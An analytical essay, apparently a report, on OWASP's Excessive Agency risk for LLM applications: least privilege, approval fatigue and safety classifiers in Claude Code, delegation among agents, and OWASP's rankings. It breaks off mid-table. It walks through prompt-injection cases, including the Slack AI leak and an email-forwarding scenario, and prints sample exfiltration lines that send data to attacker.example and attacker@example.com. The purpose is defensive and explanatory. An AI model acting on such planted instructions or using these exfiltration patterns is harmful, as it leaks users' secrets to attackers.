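Excessive Agency includes some advice from the earlier plugin entry, but it covers more than the design of tools. In LLM06:2025, OWASP defines it as the vulnerability that allows damaging actions in response to "unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated outputs" from a model, whatever the cause. The cause could be instructions an attacker planted in an email, something the model made up, or a developer's confusing prompt.

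Because the definition does not depend on why the model fails, developers can look for the weakness without predicting how the model will fail. They can list every request the application would carry out and assume that the model makes the worst one. A support assistant that only needs to read customer records but can also delete them has the weakness even if the model has never tried to delete anything. A more reliable model would make a deletion less likely, but the assistant would still be able to delete records.

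Android Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities*, Google's advice for phone app developers, focuses more on attackers, but it still places the core problem in the application, where the scope of the model's actions is "too broad and poorly controlled".

OWASP's wording is slightly too narrow because it covers only cases in which the model has malfunctioned. If a user asks an assistant to clear out old projects, the model may reasonably delete every folder that has not changed for two years, including one the user wanted to keep. A confirmation step would prevent that loss.

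OWASP traces Excessive Agency to excessive functionality, permissions or autonomy, and an application can have all three. According to SC Media, the 2026 edition still describes the risk this way.

### Functions the task does not need

In OWASP's main example of excessive functionality, a developer wants an agent to read documents from a repository and installs a third-party extension that can also change and delete them, which the agent doesn't need to do. An extension left over from a trial causes the same problem, and developers are more likely to overlook it because nobody uses it any more.

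OWASP recommends giving the model as few extensions as possible, each with as few functions as possible. A developer may be unable to remove a deletion function from someone else's extension, but the application's code can block calls to it. Leaving the function out of the prompt is not enough, because the model may still generate the name `delete_document` or copy it from an attacker's text. An application that runs any function it recognises would then delete the document.

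OWASP also advises against open-ended extensions. An application that needs to save its output to a file could use a shell extension, but that extension could also run any other command available to the application. A function such as `save_report(name, text)` can only save reports, provided it rejects file names that point outside the reports folder.

### Access rights the task does not need

Permissions determine what an extension can do in another system. OWASP gives the example of an extension that only reads data but connects to the database with an account that can also insert, update and delete it. In another example, an extension for reading the current user's files logs in with an account that can open every user's files.

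The second example shows why limiting an extension's functions is not enough. Even if the extension has only the `read_document` function that the task needs, it returns a colleague's file when the model supplies the wrong document number. OWASP recommends running each action as the user who asked for it, with the minimum access necessary, so that the document store refuses the request.

For databases, OWASP describes an agent that recommends products and needs to read only one table. The database administrator can enforce this with a single command:

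`GRANT SELECT ON products TO recommender;`

If the `recommender` account has no other rights, the database rejects any attempt to change prices or read customer records, whatever the extension sends.

Functionality and permissions are easy to confuse. *Excessive Agency in LLMs*, a guide from the monitoring software vendor Coralogix, uses the database account as an example of both. MITRE lists "Excessive Agency" as an alternative name for CWE-250, its entry on software that runs with more privilege than it needs. MITRE's note mentions functionality and permissions but not autonomy, presumably because a missing approval step gives the software no extra privilege.

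Excessive permissions can also come from a platform's default settings. Researchers found they could weaponize agents on Vertex AI, a Google cloud service for building and running them, because the agents had excessive permissions. Google has since addressed the problem, and OWASP cited the case in a draft of the 2026 entry. Developers who use such a service should check which identity it assigns to their agent and what that identity can access, since they may not have chosen either.

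### Actions without an independent check

Excessive autonomy means an application carries out high-impact actions without independent verification. OWASP's example is an extension that deletes a user's documents without asking the user to confirm.

OWASP recommends requiring human approval, either in the extension or in the system that carries out the action. For example, an application that writes social media posts should ask for approval inside the function that publishes them, so the model cannot publish without it.

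The approval also has to come from outside the model. A function such as `delete_document(id=12, confirmed=true)` offers no protection if the model fills in both values. The application itself should record the user's click and tie it to the exact request, so that approval to delete document 12 does not also cover document 13.

Complete mediation, in which the receiving system checks every request against policy, applies to all three causes. The system can reject a call to a function the agent should not use, access to a file the user may not open, or a payment nobody has approved.

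### Three ways to stop a mailbox theft

OWASP's main scenario combines the three causes. A personal assistant summarizes incoming email, but the developer has chosen an extension that can also send messages. An attacker emails the user with hidden instructions to search the inbox for sensitive information and forward it. When the user asks for a summary, the model might generate these two requests:

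`search_mail(query="password")`

`send_mail(to="attacker@example.com", body="...")`

OWASP offers three remedies, any one of which would stop the forwarding:

- With an extension that can only read mail, the application receives a request for `send_mail`, finds no such function and returns an error.
- With read-only access to the mailbox, the function exists and the application runs it. The mail server then refuses to send the message because the assistant's access token covers only reading.
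- With a manual "send" step, the application shows the message as a draft. The user sees an unfamiliar address and does not send it.

The manual step is the least dependable of these remedies because it relies on the user noticing a problem, but it is the only one that suits an assistant that also has to answer mail. A developer who wants only summaries should use both a read-only extension and read-only access, since each still works if the other fails.

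Citadelo's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a summary by a security testing company, describes a worse version of the permissions problem. If the extension does not run as the current user, an attacker may be able to send email as anyone in the company. Asking one user to approve messages would not restrict the extension's underlying access.

None of the remedies stops the model from reading the sensitive mail, so the information could still leak another way. In EchoLeak, for example, Copilot leaked data through an image URL without sending any email. Read-only access therefore prevents the theft only if the assistant also cannot fetch arbitrary URLs and the client does not load images from them.

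### An incident without an attacker

Coralogix mentions an incident at the software company PocketOS in which a coding agent ran into a credential mismatch, found an access token in an unrelated file, and deleted a production volume, the storage behind a live service. The cloud company Railway hosted the volume.

Nobody had planted instructions, so a filter would have had nothing to detect. The agent could read unrelated files, which gave it access to the token, and the token had permission to delete live data. The deletion went ahead without an effective independent check. A more restricted token would have prevented it, as would a rule at the hosting company requiring the account owner to confirm the deletion of a production volume.

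The case also shows that an agent's permissions can be wider than the ones its developer assigned. An agent that can read files and contact other services effectively has every credential it can find in those files. Giving the agent its own read-only token does little to restrict it if it can also read an administrator's token. Developers therefore have to remove such credentials or run the agent in an environment without them.

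### Why a limit on each refund is not enough

In version 0.5, OWASP described a scenario in which a customer talks the model into refunding 100 years of fees, and recommended a one-month limit in the refund API. If the fee were $20 a month, for example, the API would reject a request for the full $24,000 but accept one for $20.

A manipulated model can repeat the $20 request 1,200 times, which gives the customer the full $24,000 while keeping every payment within the limit. The API therefore also needs a cumulative limit, such as $20 per customer per year. The table compares the two attacks under different controls.

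| Control | One request for $24,000 | 1,200 requests for $20 |
|---|---|---|
| Limit in the system prompt | Depends on the model | Depends on the model |
| $20 limit on each request | Pays nothing | Pays $24,000 |
| $20 limit on each request, ten requests an hour | Pays nothing | Pays $24,000 over about five days |
| $20 limit per customer per year | Pays nothing | Pays $20 |

To enforce the cumulative limit, the application should take the customer's identity from the login session, because a model that supplies the customer number could count each refund against a different account's limit. The API also has to check the total and record the new payment in one operation. Otherwise, hundreds of requests that arrive together could all pass before the API has recorded the first payment. An attacker with 50 accounts could still collect $1,000, so the company may want a daily limit for all customers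 combined.

Even then, the customer may get $20 without having a valid complaint. The limit only keeps the loss small.

### Preventing damage and limiting it

The refund case shows how much OWASP's two damage-limiting measures, monitoring and rate limiting, can help. With refunds limited to ten an hour, the company loses $200 an hour. If an employee notices after eight hours and switches the assistant off, the loss is $1,600. If nobody is monitoring the assistant, the rate limit only delays the full loss.

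Monitoring likewise depends on a response. Coralogix, which has a commercial interest in monitoring, acknowledges that an agent with deletion rights will still delete things while monitoring software records its actions. The records are useful afterwards for working out what happened and which permissions to remove.

Rate limits are least useful when one action does most of the harm. OWASP's mailbox scenario originally involved spam, where a limit on outgoing mail helps. In the 2025 edition, OWASP changed the attack to information theft but kept the advice about rate limiting. One message can contain everything the attacker wants, so limiting the assistant to ten messages an hour might make no difference.

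In a draft of the 2026 entry, OWASP expanded rate limiting to include circuit breakers, which stop an agent or call in a person when the agent passes a threshold. The threshold could be a number of calls or a running total, such as the amount refunded. OWASP still listed this among the measures that only limit damage. That classification is right for a threshold that triggers a review after unusual activity, but a fixed annual limit in the refund API prevents any refund that would exceed it.

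### What changed between editions

The three root causes and most of the controls have stayed the same since version 0.9. The table shows some of the smaller changes.

| Part of the entry | Version 0.5 | Version 1.1 | 2025 edition |
|---|---|---|---|
| Actions that need human approval | All | All | High-impact ones |
| Harm in the mailbox scenario | Spam | Spam | Theft of information |
| Compromised peer agent named as a trigger | No | No | Yes |

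The most significant practical change was to the approval rule. In version 1.1, OWASP told developers to have a person approve "all actions before they are taken". Taken literally, this would require a person to give 40 approvals for an assistant to summarize 40 emails. An example of excessive autonomy in the same version referred only to "high-impact actions", so the advice did not match the description of the weakness. The 2025 edition removed this inconsistency.

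However, developers have to decide which actions count as high-impact. Citadelo's suggestions are sending, deleting, paying, deploying code and changing permissions. Coralogix recommends stricter approval for actions that are more damaging or harder to undo. Either approach can miss a series of small actions. A $20 refund may seem too minor to need approval, and so may each of the 1,200 refunds in the earlier example.

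The 2025 edition also added compromised peer agents to the possible causes of bad output, which already included malicious plugins in version 1.1. The addition reflects multi-agent systems, in which one agent's output becomes another's input. A request to an agent is not necessarily safe just because it comes from inside the same company's system.

According to Citadelo, OWASP changed few of the measures in 2026. Invicti reports that the entry now refers readers to a separate OWASP list for agentic applications, which covers models that use tools, keep memory between sessions and act on other systems.

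### When one agent acts for another

A chain of agents can exceed a user's authority even if each agent follows its own rules. During work on the 2026 edition, the contributor xmuruaga (2026) proposed an example in *LLM06*. An employee who is not allowed to approve refunds asks a support agent to prepare a large one. The support agent passes the task to a finance agent, which runs under a privileged account. The finance agent treats the support agent as trusted and completes the refund.

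Suppose the finance agent can approve refunds of up to $10,000, and the employee, whose own limit is zero, asks for $5,000. The payment is within the finance agent's limit, and the support agent is allowed to send it requests. If the finance agent approves the refund, it is a confused deputy, and this can happen without any prompt injection.

Xmuruaga proposes carrying the original user's identity and permissions through the whole chain. The payments system could then apply the lowest limit of anyone involved, which here is zero, so it would refuse the refund or send it to a manager for approval. The proposal was still open in June 2026, and Citadelo's summary of the published edition does not mention delegation, so OWASP may not have adopted it.

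A line of text saying who made the request would not be reliable, because a manipulated support agent could name a manager instead. The finance agent needs proof that other agents cannot alter, such as a digitally signed token. Okta, which sells identity software, warns that ordinary OAuth tokens do not record the history of delegation. By the third handover, there may be no cryptographic link to the user who started the task.

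Okta recommends narrowing permissions at each step. Some newer token formats, including Macaroons and Biscuits, let an agent add restrictions to a token before passing it on. For example, a support agent with a token for all of a customer's orders could restrict it to one order without contacting the service that issued it. The next agent could restrict the token further but not restore the original access.

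Passing on the user's identity does not solve every case. If a manager with refund rights asks the support agent to read a customer's complaint, hidden instructions in the complaint could cause the agent to issue a refund under the manager's name. The 2023 attack on ChatGPT's plugins worked the same way. An agent that runs on a schedule may have no current user, so it needs its own account with narrow rights.

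### How well people review an agent's requests

Measurements from Claude Code suggest that human approval often works badly as a control. Until August 2026, Claude Code normally asked users for approval before it ran commands or changed files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, from March 2026, describes the resulting "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve.

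Resilient Cyber, a security newsletter, reported Anthropic's figure that users approved 93 percent of these prompts and argued that many approvals were not meaningful reviews. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reports a figure of 97 percent by August. These numbers suggest, but do not prove, that people were careless. If 97 percent of the requests were safe, a perfect reviewer would also approve 97 percent, and Anthropic says that most were probably routine.

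A test with commands known to be dangerous is more informative. According to Hyrax, a software vendor, Anthropic published the results of such a test when it changed the default. Human testers caught 143 of 1,053 dangerous commands (13.6 percent), and an automated classifier caught 937 of the same commands (89 percent). The testers' rate fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed the same.

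Hyrax attributes the decline to approval fatigue. But fatigue cannot be the whole explanation, because the testers missed more than four-fifths of the dangerous commands even near the start. Many people may not recognise a dangerous command. Asking for approval less often would help with fatigue, but users also need to see what a command will do, such as how many files it will delete and where they are.

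Develeap's *Claude Code Sandboxing* describes a developer who asked Claude to organize packages in an old repository and approved the cleanup command it suggested. The command ended in `~/`, which a shell interprets as the user's home folder, and it erased the developer's documents and saved passwords. The approval prompt showed the command, but the important part was only two characters long. A warning that the command would delete the entire home folder would have been much harder to miss.

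Hyrax also reports that users reject 39 percent of the plans Claude Code proposes and infers that they read plans more carefully than individual prompts. That may be true, but users could also be rejecting safe plans because they want a different approach. Plan review still seems promising because a plan's purpose is easier to judge than a single command's. The application would then have to keep the agent's later actions within the approved plan.

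The results may not apply to every kind of approval, because an unfamiliar email recipient is easier to spot than an error in a shell command. Anthropic also ran the comparison on its own product, and the results depend on which dangerous commands it chose.

The classifier is still a serious alternative to constant approval prompts. Claude Code's auto mode uses it to determine which actions can go ahead, and returns to manual approval after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. But the classifier also missed 116 dangerous commands in the test. If people and the classifier made their mistakes independently, using both would have caught about 90.5 percent of the dangerous commands, only slightly more than the classifier alone. Restrictions on functions and permissions are therefore still needed for the commands that both would miss.

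### Fewer prompts through sandboxing

Restricting what an agent can access also reduces how often it has to ask for permission. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, from October 2025, reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts in Claude Code by 84 percent in the company's internal use. Claude Code could work freely within set boundaries, so the remaining prompts were more likely to deserve attention.

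This figure measures interruptions, not how much damage the sandbox prevented. The protection depends on what the developer leaves inside the sandbox. Anthropic warns in its documentation that an agent with network access can still leak any data it can read, and that one with write access to the project folder can still change the code there. A sandbox might have protected the home folder in the Develeap case, but it would not protect a project's only copy if the agent could delete it.

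Claude Code's built-in sandbox restricts shell commands, but its file tools and any MCP servers still run directly on the user's machine. Running the entire program in a container or virtual machine restricts those as well.

InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that Anthropic now argues for fixed limits on an agent's files, network and execution environment, so that safety does not depend only on prompts or the model's own safeguards. Anthropic had to revise some of its designs after failures, some of which involved network routes it had deliberately allowed. Copilot's leaks through approved Microsoft services were similar.

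### Whether narrow access makes agents less useful

Some critics think OWASP's approach restricts agents too much. Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, told ReversingLabs that a system needs considerable agency to find and repair its own security flaws, and that limiting it would leave organisations with less capable and less secure systems. He also argued that nobody can approve an agent's behaviour in advance, because the agent generates it afresh each time. He would rather detect failures quickly and let the system adapt so they don't recur.

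Maccherone worries that security teams will respond to OWASP's advice by adding more approval steps and policy engines. OWASP has moved towards more enforcement. In September 2026, it announced that it had received the Agent Control Standard as a donation, to extend its guidance on agents towards controls that operate while the agents run.

In the same article, Dave Hayes, a vice president at the identity software company FusionAuth, argued for narrow access because permissions can be predictable even though a model is not. He said an agent's credential should grant access only to what the agent needs, expire quickly and be easy to revoke. Narrow access limits the damage if an agent is fooled, he said, because the agent can reach one record instead of a whole database.

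Hayes has the better argument where mistakes are hard to undo. If a database rejects deletions, nobody has to predict why an agent might request one. Learning from failure works well when the agent can try again, but it does not bring back a company's only copy of its data. Maccherone is right that reviewing each action is a poor way to control an agent, and the test results from Claude Code support him, but they are not evidence against limiting what an agent can access.

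The drawback of narrow access is that developers have to write a separate function for each task, and the agent cannot handle requests they did not foresee. Sandboxes also take work because, as Anthropic notes, each new capability needs configuring. A coding agent needs to run many different commands, so replacing its shell with a few narrow functions would make it much less useful.

For such an agent, it makes more sense to keep the broad tools and restrict where they work. A security repair agent could have a full shell in an isolated copy of the system, where it could change code and run tests without asking for approval. It would not hold production credentials, and a separate process would check its changes before deploying them. The agent would keep most of the freedom Maccherone wants, and a bad command could damage only the copy.

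Greater autonomy may also make developers more productive. Anthropic says that business customers who use auto mode complete about 25 percent more pull requests (proposed changes to a codebase), though the difference may partly reflect which customers chose to adopt it. An agent that can work for hours without asking for approval is valuable, and a company can allow this more safely if the agent has no access to live customer data.

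## Which entry an attack belongs to

In LLM06:2025, OWASP distinguishes Excessive Agency from output handling, which it describes as "concerned with insufficient scrutiny of LLM outputs". Excessive Agency concerns too much power to act on those outputs. Many attacks exploit both faults, but an application can have either one alone. A chatbot that displays unencoded text but cannot call any functions has only an output-handling fault. An agent whose requests all follow a strict schema, but that has unnecessary permission to delete live data, has only excessive agency.

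### Removing one fault at a time

One way to classify an attack is to remove a single fault and ask whether the harm would still have happened. The model's bad output has to stay the same, because otherwise the answer would always be that the model should have behaved better. If a proper check on the output would have prevented the harm, the attack belongs under Improper Output Handling. If removing a function, narrowing a permission or adding an approval step would have prevented it, the attack belongs under Excessive Agency. Some attacks belong under both.

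OWASP does not state this test, but it reasons similarly in its mailbox scenario, where it lists three changes that would each have prevented the theft. The table applies the test to cases based on OWASP's scenarios.

| Harm | If the application checked the output | If the application had less power | Entry |
|---|---|---|---|
| A chat feature deletes every table in a database | Prevented: it accepts only read queries | Prevented: its account is read-only | Both |
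| A model's reply runs a script in a web page | Prevented: it encodes or sanitizes the reply | Not prevented: the model calls no functions | Improper Output Handling |
| An assistant sends an email its user did not want | Not prevented: the request is well formed | Prevented: it cannot send, or has to ask first | Excessive Agency |

OWASP describes the deleted database only under Improper Output Handling, but the preventive measures it lists there do not include a restricted database account. That advice appears under Excessive Agency, so a developer who read only the first entry would miss one of the best remedies for the attack.

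In LLM06:2025, agency means the ability to call functions or interface with other systems, which a developer grants to the application. The browser's ability to run scripts in the second row doesn't fit that definition, because browsers run scripts on any page, whether or not a model wrote them. This is true even though a Content Security Policy can restrict that ability.

The email is harder to classify than the table suggests. An application could reject any message to an address outside the company, and this rule could count as scrutiny of the output or as a limit on the assistant's power. One test is whether the right check would change if the assistant had different authority. HTML encoding would be the same for any assistant, but a recipient rule depends on whom this one may write to, so it fits better under Excessive Agency. A rule that accepts only `SELECT` statements both inspects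 the text and limits what the assistant may do, so no definition will separate the entries completely.

The test can also give a wrong answer when an attack has two routes. Suppose an assistant can send email and its chat client loads images from any address. An attacker tells the model to leak a password both ways. Removing either the send function or the image loading leaves the other route open, so neither fault seems to matter, although both do. Testing each route as a separate harm avoids this error.

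### The Slack AI leak

Slack AI answers questions about the messages in a company's Slack workspace. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published on 20 August 2024, describes how an attacker with an account in a workspace could obtain secrets from private channels they had never joined.

In the demonstration, a developer kept an API key, a password that programs use, in a private channel with no other members. The attacker created a public channel, also with no other members, and posted a message there. The message told the model to answer questions about the key with an error notice and a link. Simplified, the link looked like this:

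`[click here to reauthenticate](https://attacker.example?secret=confetti)`

The message also told the model to replace "confetti" with the real key. The attacker did not need to know the key or have access to the private channel.

Slack AI searches all public channels, including those the user has not joined. When the developer later asked it for the key, it retrieved both messages and put them in the same prompt. The model followed the attacker's instructions and showed the developer an error with a link to log in again. Clicking the link sent the key to the attacker's server, where it appeared in the log.

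The attack was also hard to trace. Slack AI is supposed to cite every message that contributed to an answer, but it cited only the developer's private channel. The attacker's message did not appear on the first page of search results either. In a second demonstration, which used an ordinary phishing link containing no private data, Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel.

OWASP lists PromptArmor's report as the first reference under Excessive Agency, without explaining why. By the removal test, the attack belongs mostly under Insecure Output Handling. The data left through a displayed link, as in the 2024 Copilot leak. If Slack had removed links to unapproved domains from the model's replies, the developer would have seen a puzzling error message and the key would have stayed in Slack.

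Reducing Slack AI's power would have helped much less. It had no function for sending data that Slack could have removed. Running the search under the developer's own identity would have changed nothing, because the developer was entitled to read both messages. Restricting the search to channels the developer had joined would have stopped this version of the attack, but it would have made the search less useful, and an attacker could still post the same message in a shared channel. There was arguably already an approval step, because no data was sent until the developer clicked the link. The link text hid the address, though hovering over the link revealed it.

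The Slack AI leak is a much closer match for Improper Output Handling than for Excessive Agency. It resembles OWASP's website summarizer scenario under Improper Output Handling, where the missing control is validation or filtering of the output. Willison (2024) also describes the Slack flaw in terms of a Markdown link that passes private data to the attacker when someone clicks it. The case for Excessive Agency is that a stranger's message could influence what Slack AI did with private data, which makes it a confused deputy, but that is true of most indirect prompt injection. A company that treated the leak as a problem of excessive agency might review all of Slack AI's access rights, find them in order, and leave the link in place.

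### Slack's response

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Slack on 14 August and answered two rounds of questions. On 19 August, Slack replied that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information in PromptArmor's first video came from a public channel, that any workspace member could search for such messages, and that this was "intended behavior."

Slack's reply addressed a different complaint. Slack was right that members may read public channels, but the public message contained only the attacker's instruction, and the key came from a private channel.

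PromptArmor published its report the next day, and Slack released a patch the same day. In a statement on 21 August, Slack (2024) said that "under very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an account in the same workspace could phish users for certain data, and that it had no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data. Slack did not say in the statement what the patch changed, so the statement does not show which fault Slack considered responsible.

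The attack worked only if the victim asked a question that retrieved the attacker's message, the model followed the message's instructions, and the victim clicked. But "phish" understates the problem, because phishing usually requires the victim to type a password into a false page, while this attack needed nothing more from the victim after the click.

On 14 August, Slack AI began to include uploaded files in its answers, which may also have removed the attacker's need for an account. PromptArmor warned that an employee could download a PDF containing instructions in white text and upload it to Slack. It considered this highly likely to work but had finished its tests before the change.

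### Where OWASP's own text blurs the line

Each entry's reference list includes an attack that also fits the other entry. Excessive Agency lists the Slack attack that used a displayed link. LLM05:2025, the output-handling entry, cites a 2023 demonstration in which a web page made ChatGPT read a user's email through a plugin, an attack that depended heavily on what the plugins could do and whose requests they accepted.

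The first attack scenario in LLM05:2025, described earlier, is similarly hard to place. A chatbot's unchecked response shuts down an extension that also serves a more privileged model. A shutdown request from that model might be valid, so a check on the text alone would have to accept the command from both models or reject it from both. The extension also has to check which model is calling and what that model may do, which is a question of permissions.

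The 2025 edition also uses outdated names to distinguish its entries. LLM06:2025 contrasts Excessive Agency with "Insecure Output Handling", and LLM05:2025 contrasts output handling with "Overreliance", but neither name is on the 2025 list. Tenable's *What You Must Know About the OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications* confirms that Misinformation replaced Overreliance. More than a year later, a slide in *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) repeated the contrast with Overreliance while listing Misinformation among the ten current entries.

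OWASP seems to have fixed this in 2026. According to Respan, Improper Output Handling now covers unsafe use of output, Misinformation covers incorrect output, and checking the model's input belongs under Prompt Injection. The last change would also correct the script scenario in LLM05:2025, which wrongly attributes the problem to prompts.

### Whether "least privilege" would be a better name

In his January 2025 review of the 2025 edition, Rich Harang called the output handling entry "very good" and its main advice, to know what consumes a model's output and neutralise that output accordingly, "critically important". But he also found "a bit of confusion with least-privilege issues" in the entry. He gave no example, though the shutdown scenario fits.

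Harang also praised the measures under Excessive Agency, but said OWASP should rename the entry "Failure to Implement Least Privilege". Security engineers already know the term "least privilege", and it names the missing control. "Excessive agency" could easily be taken to mean that the model has too much will of its own. Harang's proposed name is more accurate for needless functions and access rights.

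Least privilege works less well against excessive autonomy. An assistant that tidies a mailbox needs permission to delete messages, so it can satisfy least privilege and still delete an important message without asking. It lacks a check at the moment of deletion.

Harang could reply that privileges can be conditional. The assistant might have no permission to delete anything until the user approves a particular deletion, and then receive a single-use token for that message. On this view, an assistant that can delete without approval has more privilege than it needs, and his term covers all three root causes.

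That position is consistent, and it is a good way to build an approval step. But most developers who read "least privilege" would probably review only their accounts and tokens. Harang's own summary of the preventive measures also includes checking each action against security policy, which goes beyond the usual meaning of least privilege. His other suggestion, to think "least privilege" while reading the entry, keeps most of the benefit without narrowing the title.

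### When a wrong answer becomes an action

When Overreliance became Misinformation, the focus moved from the people and systems that trust an answer to the answer itself. The 2026 edition partly reverses this. Infosecurity Magazine reports that Misinformation now covers output credible enough to influence a human decision, an automated workflow or an agent's action.

The new definition overlaps with Excessive Agency, which has always included actions that result from a model's mistakes. Invicti gives the example of a developer's assistant that reviews a codebase and files reports on anything that looks broken. The assistant files a critical report on a vulnerability that does not exist, and an on-call engineer spends three hours looking for it.

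The removal test changes slightly here because, under Misinformation, the output itself is the fault. If the assistant had assessed the code correctly, it would not have filed a false report, so Misinformation applies. If the assistant had needed approval to file critical reports, a developer might have caught the error, so Excessive Agency also applies. Improper Output Handling does not apply, because the report could be well formed and safe to display. If the assistant had just mentioned the supposed flaw in a chat, and the engineer had decided to investigate, only Misinformation would apply.

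The controls for the two entries can also catch different mistakes. Suppose a support assistant misreads a delivery date and proposes a $20 refund for a late parcel. The refund is within every limit, and an employee who sees only "parcel arrived nine days late" will probably approve it, so the company pays even though the approval step worked as designed. Preventing this requires checking the claim against the delivery record.

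OWASP's advice on Misinformation includes grounding answers in authoritative sources and, in Infosecurity Magazine's summary, having the model verify claims before acting. A model that has misread a date may misread it again, so comparing the dates in the application's code would be safer. If there is no record to compare, the company has to rely on human judgment or accept small losses.

Harang doubted that Misinformation was strictly a security issue and would have left it off the list. His objection is reasonable for answers that only people read. When software acts on an answer, the risk is clearly a security matter, but Excessive Agency already covers the action. In those cases, the Misinformation entry mainly adds the need to check that the answer is correct, as well as that the action is authorized.

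### The separate list for agents

OWASP published a Top 10 for Agentic Applications in December 2025. In the announcement, Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario (2025) wrote that the project had already covered excessive agency but needed to go deeper into agent security.

In the 2026 edition of the language-model list, OWASP tries to explain what each of the two lists covers. According to Respan, the language-model list applies while the model is a component inside an application, and the agentic list applies once the model acts on its own account, with tools, memory and effects on other systems. OWASP acknowledges that many incidents fall on the boundary and advises people to read both lists.

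Excessive Agency does not fit this division well. Its definition depends on a model's ability to call functions, so every application with the weakness has at least one feature of an actor. OWASP kept the entry on the component list anyway. An application can also have some features of an actor without the others. For example, an assistant that issues refunds but forgets each conversation has tools and consequences but no memory.

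Mend.io, a software security company, recommends asking whether each AI component can call tools, whether it keeps information between sessions, and what it can write to. The answers show which controls the component needs, even when it is unclear which entry on the lists applies.

The three agentic entries closest to output handling and excessive agency are Tool Misuse and Exploitation (ASI02), Identity and Privilege Abuse (ASI03) and Unexpected Code Execution (ASI05).

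Tool misuse occurs when an agent does harm with tools it is allowed to use. In an example from Sotiropoulos, a tool accepts the instruction to "clean old items and provide a summary". An attacker's text makes the agent treat current records as old. The agent deletes them, then uses its permitted email function to send a summary and the affected data outside the company. A tool with a fixed rule for what counts as old would have prevented the deletion, and requiring approval for outside recipients would probably have prevented the leak.

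The company Fidelis Security says OWASP presents ASI02 as the agentic version of Excessive Agency. But Fidelis's own example is a straightforward case of excessive permissions: a support bot can issue refunds because its token gives it more access than the task needs. Sotiropoulos emphasises harm done within policy and with the right permissions. On that reading, ASI02 is most useful for failures that least privilege misses, including excessive autonomy and tools that accept instructions as vague as "clean old items".

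Privilege abuse corresponds more closely to excessive permissions, but it also includes permissions an agent acquires while it runs. Sotiropoulos describes a coding assistant with a powerful GitHub token. During a handover, the token leaks to a second agent that was supposed to have few rights. An attacker then gets the second agent to delete a private repository or make it public. A developer who reviewed the second agent's settings beforehand would have found nothing wrong. Limiting the token to one task, and having GitHub reject it from any other agent, would have prevented the attack.

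Unexpected code execution overlaps with both older entries. Sotiropoulos cites an attack by the research firm Positive Security on Auto-GPT, an early open-source agent. Auto-GPT visited a web page containing instructions to download and run a script. It followed them, and the script exploited configuration mistakes in Auto-GPT's container to run code on the host machine.

The attack caused two separate harms. The script ran inside the container because the agent executed text from an untrusted page, which is an output-handling failure. It reached the host because the container gave it more access than it needed. Correcting the container's configuration would have prevented only the harm to the host. For an agent whose job is to run code, that may still be the more important fix, since no check can reliably recognise every dangerous program before it runs.

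## How votes and incident records rank the two risks

Until 2026, OWASP ranked the entries by experts' judgment alone, so it didn't need to count attacks. The 2026 edition added incident records, but an attack that fits two entries is hard to count. Over three editions, the two risks have moved in opposite directions in the ranking.

| Edition | Output handling | Excessive agency | Basis of the ranking |
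|---|---|---|---|
| 2023 | 2 | 8 | Practitioners' judgment |
| 2025 | 5 | 6 | Practitioners' judgment |
| 2026 | 10 | 3 | About 75 percent vote, 25 percent incident records |

The 2023 positions, which still appear on OWASP's *LLM02* page, had not changed since version 0.5. Constantin reports both moves in 2026.

### What a rank meant before 2026

In the first two editions, a rank was only a judgment of a risk's importance relative to the others. When the project drew up its first list, there were too few cases to rank ten risks by. Wilson told ReversingLabs that the risks were purely theoretical at that point, which slightly overstates it, since Snyk had published the LangChain code-execution flaw a month before the project began.

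A risk's rank can also change because other entries move or are removed. Excessive agency rose two places in the 2025 edition. It gained one because OWASP widened denial of service into Unbounded Consumption and moved it from fourth place to tenth, and the other because OWASP dropped Insecure Plugin Design, which had been seventh.

Output handling fell three places in the same edition, as sensitive information disclosure, supply chain risks and data poisoning moved above it. Its decline therefore began before OWASP used any incident data.

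### What the 2026 incident records contain

For the 2026 edition, the project collected 7,714 records from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI. According to ReversingLabs, the project then built classifiers, programs that read each record and assign it to a category. The classifiers sorted 6,639 of the records, or 86 percent. The other 1,075 lacked enough detail to sort and did not affect the ranking.

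The 86 percent is the share of records that the classifiers could sort, and neither ReversingLabs nor Respan reports how accurately they sorted them. Errors could matter a good deal. If the classifiers put 10 percent of the records in the wrong category, for example, about 664 would be misplaced, as many as each entry would have if ten entries shared the records equally.

The word "incident" also covers both product flaws and harmful events. Vulnerability databases list the flaws, which researchers often find before anyone exploits them. EchoLeak, for example, has a public vulnerability record but no known victims. Harm databases list events that did damage, such as the deletion of PocketOS's production volume. That deletion involved a powerful access token left in one company's files, which is not the kind of product flaw that vulnerability databases normally list.

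The result depends on how many records came from vulnerability databases and how many from a harm database. Vulnerability databases should contain many output-handling flaws, which are often ordinary product bugs, while a harm database is more likely to contain wrong answers that somebody relied on. ReversingLabs does not report the split.

### How the vote and the records were combined

The project leaders gave the vote three-quarters of the weight because the list is a consensus product, and they did not want one noisy year of data to outweigh the votes of hundreds of practitioners. ReversingLabs reports that they consider the remaining quarter, given to incident records, enough to move an entry by a tier when the vote and the records are far apart. Wilson said this was the first time in three years that the project had enough data to influence its decisions.

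The published accounts give these weights but no formula. The most obvious method would be to average each entry's two positions, but the results for prompt injection make that very unlikely. It came first in the vote. By incident count alone it would have missed the top ten, according to Infosecurity Magazine, so its position there was eleventh or lower. (OWASP must therefore have sorted the incidents into at least eleven categories.) Its best possible average would be:

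`0.75 × 1 + 0.25 × 11 = 3.5`

A hypothetical entry that came second on both measures would score 2.0 and take first place. Sensitive information disclosure, which finished second overall, may have been close to this example. Infosecurity Magazine reports that practitioners' views of that risk corresponded closely to the incident records. If the risk ranked the same on both measures, prompt injection could have beaten it only if it ranked fourth or lower on each.

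Prompt injection could stay first if OWASP averaged scores instead of positions, because scores show how far one risk leads another. The numbers below are invented.

| Entry | Vote score | Incident score | Combined score |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | 100 | 5 | 76.25 |
| Sensitive information disclosure | 80 | 60 | 75 |

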